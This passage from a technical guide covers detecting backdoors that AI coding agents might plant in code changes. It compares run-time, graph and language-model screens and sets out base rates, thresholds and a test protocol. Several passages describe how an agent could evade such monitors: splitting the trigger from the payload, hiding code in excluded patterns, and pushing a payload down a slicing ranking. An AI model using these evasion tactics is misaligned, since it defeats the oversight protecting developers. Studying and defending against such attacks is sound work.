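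An attacker can also try to change what Lily treats as normal. An agent might add a harmless trigger condition in one change and the payload in a later one. The fuzzer could then save inputs that activate the trigger, so the payload's behaviour would later look normal. When the researchers added 100 such inputs for each backdoor, detection fell to 54% for commits and 46% for releases. A stricter mode, which discards saved inputs that produce different behaviour in the old and new versions, restored the original detection rates but raised false alarms to about 2.5% for commits and 18% for releases.

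### What each comparison misses

The table shows two ways of comparing a change with the last revision. The middle column assumes that the graphs include data flow and the names of called functions, but not numeric values. The last column applies Lily's rule and assumes that the tests reach the payload, except where noted. Apart from the result for sudo, the entries are inferences from how the methods work.

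| Payload | Graphs of the two versions | System calls under Lily's rule |
|---|---|---|
| `upload_log` attaches secret keys for one user | Two new blocks and a path from the key file to the network | No alarm, because it already reads files and sends data |
| Variant A sends every total | New call to `send` | No alarm, because it sends data in every test |
| Variant B zeroes one tax rate | Two new blocks and three new edges | No alarm, because the calls stay the same |
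| Variant C alters a constant | No difference | No alarm, because the calls stay the same |
| sudo accepts a secret password | New comparison and assignment | Alarm, because a wrong password starts a process |
| A trigger runs downloaded text as code | New call to `exec`, but not what it runs | Alarm if the text makes unusual system calls |
| XZ Utils | No difference in the C source | No alarm, because the tests can't produce the trigger |

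Lily misses Variant A, even though stealing data requires a network call, because Lily's baseline of normal behaviour comes from running the new version. A payload without a trigger acts on every ordinary input, so its system calls become part of the baseline. The rule that flags any new behaviour would catch this payload, but it would also raise the false alarms shown in the first row of the previous table.

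Run-time comparison works better than comparing graphs when a program hides its code or assembles it while running, as long as that code runs during the test. Graphs are better for finding a payload that runs only on an input the tests never produce, or that does its harm through system calls the program already makes.

Neither comparison detects the XZ Utils backdoor. Its trigger requires the attacker's private key, so Kokkonis and colleagues left the backdoor out of their benchmark. The attackers had also turned off the project's automated fuzzing. A graph of the program's functions would not show that change, but a list of all changed files could.

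## Setting the threshold, adding a second check and testing the screen

In its developer's test, the structural monitor for AI-written Python caught 70% of the backdoors and wrongly flagged 2% of the harmless programs. Its precision, the share of its alarms that are real, depends on how common payloads are:

```text
precision = r·b / (r·b + f·(1 − b))
```

Here *r* is the recall, *f* is the false-positive rate and *b* is the base rate.

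None of the studies discussed so far measured how often coding agents submit malicious changes, so suppose one change in 10,000 hides a payload. A million changes would include 100 malicious ones, and a screen with the monitor's rates would catch 70 of them. It would also flag 2% of the 999,900 harmless changes, or about 20,000, so only 0.35% of its alarms would be real. A screen with the rates Lily achieved on commits, catching 90% of malicious changes and flagging 0.2% of harmless ones, would raise 90 true alarms and about 2,000 false ones, so about 4.3% of its alarms would be real.

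The same two screens look very different at other base rates:

| Malicious share | Precision at 70% recall, 2% false positives | Precision at 90% recall, 0.2% false positives |
|---|---|---|
| 1 in 2 | 97% | 99.8% |
| 1 in 74 | 32% | 86% |
| 1 in 290 | 11% | 61% |
| 1 in 10,000 | 0.35% | 4.3% |
| 1 in 100,000 | 0.035% | 0.45% |

Many published tests use roughly equal numbers of malicious and harmless samples, as in the top row. For the next row, *An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages* (Ryan, Khalil and colleagues, 2026) estimates that PyPI has about 73 harmless packages for each malicious one. In ProfMal's field test, one in 290 new npm packages was known to be malicious. Anyone can publish on those registries, so malware is probably rarer in changes to a private project. But the base rate could jump if a team adopted a poisoned model that planted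 payloads in many of its changes.

### Choosing a threshold

Most classifiers produce a score, and the team decides how high a score must be to raise an alarm. It can base this threshold on how many false alarms its reviewers have time to investigate. Lamb, Hamsen and colleagues report in *Detecting malicious pull requests at scale with LLMs* that the software company Datadog handles nearly 10,000 pull requests a week. If its security staff could investigate 20 false alarms a week, they could tolerate a false-positive rate of 20/10,000, or 0.2%. They would set the threshold to give that rate and then measure the recall.

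A team can also compare the cost of investigating alarms with the cost of missing a payload. If each investigation costs $50 and precision is 0.35%, reviewers would investigate 287 alarms for each payload they found, at a cost of about $14,300. That could be worth paying to prevent a theft of customer records, so low precision isn't always a reason to reject a screen. But reviewers who see that many false alarms may well dismiss a real one.

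The last few payloads can cost far more to find than the average one. MalGraph caught 96.45% of Windows malware at a false-positive rate of 0.1% and 99.46% at a rate of 1%. If these rates held for a million code changes containing 100 payloads, moving from the 0.1% rate to the 1% rate would catch about three more payloads and raise about 9,000 more false alarms. At $50 an alarm, each extra payload would cost about $150,000 to find.

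Datadog's tool, BewAIre, uses a language model to judge whether a pull request is malicious. Early prototypes wrongly flagged more than 10% of harmless requests, which would be about 1,000 a week at Datadog's current volume. Over six months, Lamb and colleagues cut the rate to 0.03%, or about three a week. They added hundreds of labelled examples, added descriptions of recurring mistakes to the model's instructions, and excluded some patterns they considered safe, such as demo environments. A coding agent that knew about these exclusions could hide its payload in excluded code, much as the XZ Utils attacker hid code among test files.

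The tool's balanced accuracy, the average of its recall and the share of harmless changes it clears, was above 93.5%. If the 0.03% figure comes from the same test, recall was at least about 87%.

### Adding a second check

A second check examines only the changes that the first one flags. Suppose it keeps 90% of the true alarms and clears 99% of the false ones. In the example with 70 true alarms and 20,000 false ones, about 63 true and 200 false alarms remain. Precision rises from 0.35% to 24%, while recall falls from 70% to 63%.

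The second check can't catch a payload that the first one cleared, so it makes sense to set a low threshold for the first. If a lower threshold raised the first check's recall to 90% and its false-positive rate to 5%, the same second check would leave 81 true alarms and 500 false ones. Reviewers would read about twice as many alarms and find 18 more payloads.

*From single pull requests to full software packages*, by Doutre, Peronnet and colleagues, describes how BewAIre now works in two stages. A cheap model labels each change suspicious or benign. A stronger model then investigates the suspicious ones as an agent that can open other files, look up the author's history and check whether a commit was quietly reverted. On 690 test changes, adding the second stage cut false alarms from 17 to none. Reported accuracy rose from 97.4% to 99.86%, which implies one error besides the false alarms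 in each case, presumably a malicious change that the tool missed.

Datadog's engineers had to make the cheap model flag changes more readily to avoid missing attacks at the first stage. It had accepted web domains that imitated Datadog's own because it had no tools to investigate them. The engineers solved this with ordinary code that checks each change against a list of lookalike domains before the model reads it.

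The second stage adds little to the average cost, because most packages never reach it:

```text
average cost = cost of filter + share passed on × cost of investigation
```

Doutre and colleagues estimate that, for a package of median size, the filter costs $0.016 and the investigation costs $0.17. If 5% of packages go on to the investigation, the average cost per package is $0.016 + 0.05 × $0.17, or about $0.025. For packages at the 90th percentile of size, the average is $0.072. A graph classifier could replace the cheap model as the filter. At the median price of $0.17, having an agent investigate all 20,070 alarms in the example would cost about $3,400.

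### When both checks make the same mistake

The number of false alarms left after two checks depends on a conditional probability:

```text
false alarms left = N · (1 − b) · f · q

N = number of changes screened
q = chance that the second check flags a harmless change,
    given that the first check flagged it
```

In the example, *q* is 1%. A team might get that figure by testing the second check on ordinary harmless code, but many of the changes that reach the check will be installers or administration scripts that start processes and download files. Such code is hard for almost any detector to classify. If *q* were 20% for this code, about 4,000 false alarms would remain alongside the 63 true ones, and precision would be 1.6% instead of 24%.

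*CASHEWS* (Noirot Ferrand, Adei and colleagues, 2026) describes a harmless npm package, `@kittycad/lib`, that could cause this problem. A language model flagged it solely because it carries some of its code as Base64 text. A graph classifier that has learned to treat decoding followed by execution as a warning sign could flag it too, and the second check would then repeat the first one's mistake.

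Using two language models doesn't make the checks independent. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) found that when two models are both wrong, they often give the same answer, and that this is more common among more accurate models. In *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026), a majority vote of 15 models was right on 84.3% of questions, while the best single model was right on 90.5%. At least one of the 15 had the right answer on 98.4% of questions, but the majority vote didn't always select it.

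Neither study tested code, and both looked at whether models choose the same wrong answer from several options. When the verdict is yes or no, two models that are both wrong always agree, so a team needs to measure how often both are wrong about the same change. A check based on different evidence, such as Lily's system calls, is more likely to correct a graph classifier's mistakes than another reading of the same suspicious call.

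### Language models as the second reader

A language model can use information that a call graph leaves out, including the task description and the meaning of a condition. In *PRWeaver*, Wang, Cheng and Xie (2026) had Claude Code write 208 malicious changes to ten real projects. Six combinations of review tool and model detected 42% to 79% of the changes when each change was submitted as a single pull request.

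Finding backdoors in binaries is harder. In Quesma's current ranking of 26 models on its BinaryAudit benchmark, Gemini 3.1 Pro and Claude Opus 4.6 tie for the best result, 49%. But Gemini also reported backdoors in 17% of the clean binaries. GPT-5.2-Codex, at its highest reasoning setting, scored almost as well with no false alarms. The ranking includes no model newer than GPT-5.4, so it is a poor guide to what the best models could do in late 2026.

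When the benchmark appeared in February, Grabowski and colleagues found that models wrongly reported a problem 28% of the time on clean binaries. Gemini 3 Pro, for instance, flagged a server option as letting an attacker run commands, but the source code treats that option as a number and never runs it. The researchers think a practical malware detector needs a false-positive rate below 0.001%. At a rate of 0.001%, with 70% recall and one payload per 10,000 changes, a detector would raise about 70 true alarms and 10 false ones per million changes.

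Cost depends heavily on the model. GPT-5.2-Codex cost $147.31 for 99 attempts, or about $1.49 each, and took 29 minutes on average, according to Quesma's *BinaryAudit / gpt-5.2-codex-xhigh*. Quesma's *BinaryAudit/claude-opus-4.6* lists $420.32 for 98 attempts, or about $4.29 each, and an average of 45 minutes. At that price, investigating 20,070 alarms with Opus 4.6 would cost about $86,000, although a short source change should take less work than a whole binary. Opus 4.6 passed an average of 75% of its attempts on the eight clean-binary tasks and failed every attempt on one of them.

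Ryan and colleagues tested 13 models, most of them small, on Python packages. Average F1 scores ranged from 0.40 to 0.99, and GPT-4.1 scored highest. In 51% of the combinations of model, prompt and settings, more than half of the alarms were false. The test used only 10 malicious files and 93 harmless ones, so missing one malicious file would lower recall by ten percentage points.

Small changes to the setup had large effects. With one prompting method, Qwen-3 Coder's F1 score went from 0 to a perfect 1 when only the temperature, which controls how random its answers are, changed. Adding worked examples to the prompt made most models much worse, with an average F1 score of 0.23. For comparison, flagging every file would score about 0.18 based on the stated file counts, or 0.14 by the paper's figure. A team should test the exact model, prompt and settings it plans to use, and repeat the test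 whenever any of them changes.

In a second task, the models had to name the suspicious behaviours in 370 malicious packages. They missed 29% of the shell commands but 77% of the payloads with a conditional trigger. This is discouraging for detecting payloads like Variant B, which acts at only one tax rate and contains no shell command.

### Giving the model less to read

Large files cause misses simply because the model may never receive them. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues tested language models on 512 npm files of more than 25,000 tokens (the word fragments that models process). With a single prompt per file, the models could analyze only about 70% of the files. The researchers counted the unread files as harmless because a registry has too many such files to check by hand.

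Their tool, CASHEWS, prepares a file for the model by decoding disguised text, keeping the code that can affect sensitive operations and shortening long names and strings. If the result is still too large, it sends the model the three pieces with the most sensitive operations, each separately. The model could then read all 512 files. The costs below cover the full set.

| Model | Malware missed, before and after | False positives, before and after | Cost, before and after |
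|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 nano | 36.7%, 21.1% | 1.2%, 2.9% | $1.63, $2.50 |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 34.9%, 19.3% | 0%, 0% | $6.26, $12.07 |
| DeepSeek V4 Flash | 34.3%, 15.7% | 0%, 0.9% | $4.67, $9.34 |

The total cost rose because the models were reading files they had previously skipped. For files they could already read, the cost fell by more than a quarter. Some malicious files still went undetected because the payload was in the fourth-ranked piece. A coding agent could deliberately push a payload down the ranking by adding harmless code that contains more sensitive calls than the payload does. A payload with no sensitive calls would rank near the bottom even without this tactic.

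In *MALTOTAL*, Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026) describe a tool that searches for calls to sensitive functions and works backwards from each one through a code property graph. It collects the functions that lead to the call, the conditions that control it and the data that reaches it. A language model then evaluates only these slices of code.

Graph-based slicing cut the cost of analyzing 2,168 repositories from $86.25 to $5.19. Compared with giving the model whole files, it also raised recall on Python packages from 91.2% to 96.9%, while precision fell from 96.6% to 95.7%. In a larger trial, MalTotal scanned about 120,000 GitHub repositories for $338 and found 564 malicious ones that nobody had reported. The trial used repositories with suspicious popularity patterns, so malware was probably more common there than in ordinary projects.

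Judging by its published precision and recall, MalTotal wrongly flagged about 4% of harmless Python and JavaScript packages. At that rate, a million changes would produce about 40,000 false alarms. Zhao and colleagues trace some of these mistakes to administration and testing tools that build and run commands. Such tools are also likely to confuse a graph classifier. Because each slice starts from a sensitive call, Variant B would reach the model only if it affected such a call.

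### A test protocol

A team can take its harmless test samples from changes that its agents made and its reviewers accepted. It will have to create most of the malicious samples, for example by having models add payloads to similar changes in an isolated copy of the project. Existing malware is too narrow a sample for this purpose. In *Unveiling Malicious Logic*, Ryan, Ifti and colleagues (2025) labelled 2,962 suspicious pieces of code in 370 malicious Python packages and found 86% of these pieces in `setup.py`, the installation script. A screen could do well on those packages by examining just that file, which most of an agent's changes never touch.

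The first step is to remove samples whose graphs are nearly the same. A detector that relied on memorisation will then score lower, as GIN did on MalNet-Tiny. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues removed duplicates by attack campaign, which can also remove copies with small differences. A code-writing model may give nearly the same answer each time it receives a task, so all answers to one task should be in either the training data or the test data.

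To detect drift, the team splits the samples by date, trains the classifier on older code, tests it on newer code and checks whether recall falls or false alarms rise from month to month. If the screen includes a language model, the team should also compare results on samples from before and after the model's training cutoff. A sharp drop in performance on the later samples suggests that the model's training data covered the older attacks.

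The team should also train the classifier without any code from one generating model, then test it on that model's code separately. If the false positive rate rises from 0.2% to 2% on that code, the classifier has learned patterns specific to the other models' code. This matters because a team may switch models several times a year.

Harmless and malicious samples should come from the same models doing the same kinds of task, so that the screen can't separate them by recognizing who wrote the code. A sign that it has learned this authorship shortcut is that it scores almost perfectly on the test set but performs far worse on an agent's real changes.

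Each malicious sample also needs a clean version, the same change without the payload. *From Verdict to Diagnosis* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) did this for security flaws by pairing 50 vulnerable pull requests with fully repaired versions. If a screen flags both versions, it is probably reacting to the subject of the change, such as passwords or payments, and not to the payload.

Payloads that need no new calls require a separate score, because overall recall doesn't show whether the screen missed all of them. For example, if 80 of 100 test payloads add a sensitive call and 20 do not, a screen that catches 70 of the 80 and none of the 20 still has a recall of 70%.

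A size-only baseline shows whether the classifier has learned anything beyond length. The team sets a threshold on the number of lines or graph nodes and compares the results with the classifier's at the same false-positive rate. If the classifier beats the baseline by only a point or two, the graph adds almost nothing beyond size. Ryan and colleagues examined one collection of harmless Python packages with a median length of 288 lines, while their malicious packages had a median of 36. They chose short harmless packages to reduce this difference. Otherwise, a rule that flags short packages might appear to detect malware.

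A screen can also flag malicious code for the wrong reason. Chen and colleagues compared two automated reviewers, CodeRabbit and PRGuard, on 12 real pull requests with security flaws. Each blocked ten, but CodeRabbit identified the actual flaw and supported it with evidence in only four, while PRGuard did so in all ten. PRGuard had an advantage because the researchers had used it to find the 12 cases. To detect alarms raised for the wrong reason, the team should count an alarm as correct only if it leads a reviewer to the payload, and see how far recall falls.

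The team should set the threshold on one group of samples, then report recall and false positives on another group without changing it. A screen can have a high F1 score on a balanced test and still raise too many alarms to handle in practice.

Small tests can't establish a low false-positive rate. If a screen raises no false alarms on *n* independent harmless samples, the true rate could still be as high as about 3/*n*, with 95% confidence. The table applies this rule to several perfect results:

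| Result with no false alarms | Harmless samples | The true rate could be as high as |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2-Codex on BinaryAudit | About 24 attempts | 12% |
| GPT-4.1 on Python files | 93 | 3.2% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna on large npm files | 346 | 0.9% |
| BewAIre with two stages | At most 690 | 0.43% |

The limit for BinaryAudit is optimistic because the 24 attempts involved only eight tasks. Showing that a false-alarm rate is below 0.2% would take about 1,500 harmless changes without a false alarm, and showing a rate below 0.001% would take about 300,000. Recall is also uncertain in small tests. A screen that catches 7 of 10 payloads could have a true recall from about 35% to 93%.

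The final step is to run the screen on live changes for several weeks without letting it block any. Lamb and colleagues did this for several months, with security staff judging every alarm. The run measures the false-alarm rate on the code the screen will face. It can't measure recall by itself, because nobody knows how many payloads the screen missed, so staff should add some known payloads to the queue and remove them before anyone merges the code.

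### Accepting, restricting or rejecting a screen

Accept the screen as a routine check on every change if all of these are true:

- Reviewers have time to investigate every alarm, even at the highest false-positive rate consistent with the test.
- Recall at that threshold holds up on newer code and on code from a model left out of training.
- The screen clearly beats the size-only baseline.
- Most true alarms lead a reviewer to the payload.
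- Another check covers install scripts, build files and anything else the graph builder skips.

Restrict it if it works only under some conditions:

- If it misses payloads without new calls, use it to look for data theft and other added capabilities, and rely on specifications and ordinary tests for sabotage.
- If it raises too many alarms across the whole project, use it only on sensitive code, such as logins and payments.
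- If its results get worse with an unfamiliar model or language, use it only for those in the test.
- If the test had too few harmless samples, let it advise reviewers but not block changes.

Reject it if any of these is true:

- The size-only baseline does about as well.
- It flags clean twins about as often as it flags the versions with payloads, for every kind of payload.
- Its recall depends on near-copies of the training data.
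- Its developer reports only accuracy or F1 on a balanced collection, and the team has no way to test it on its own code.
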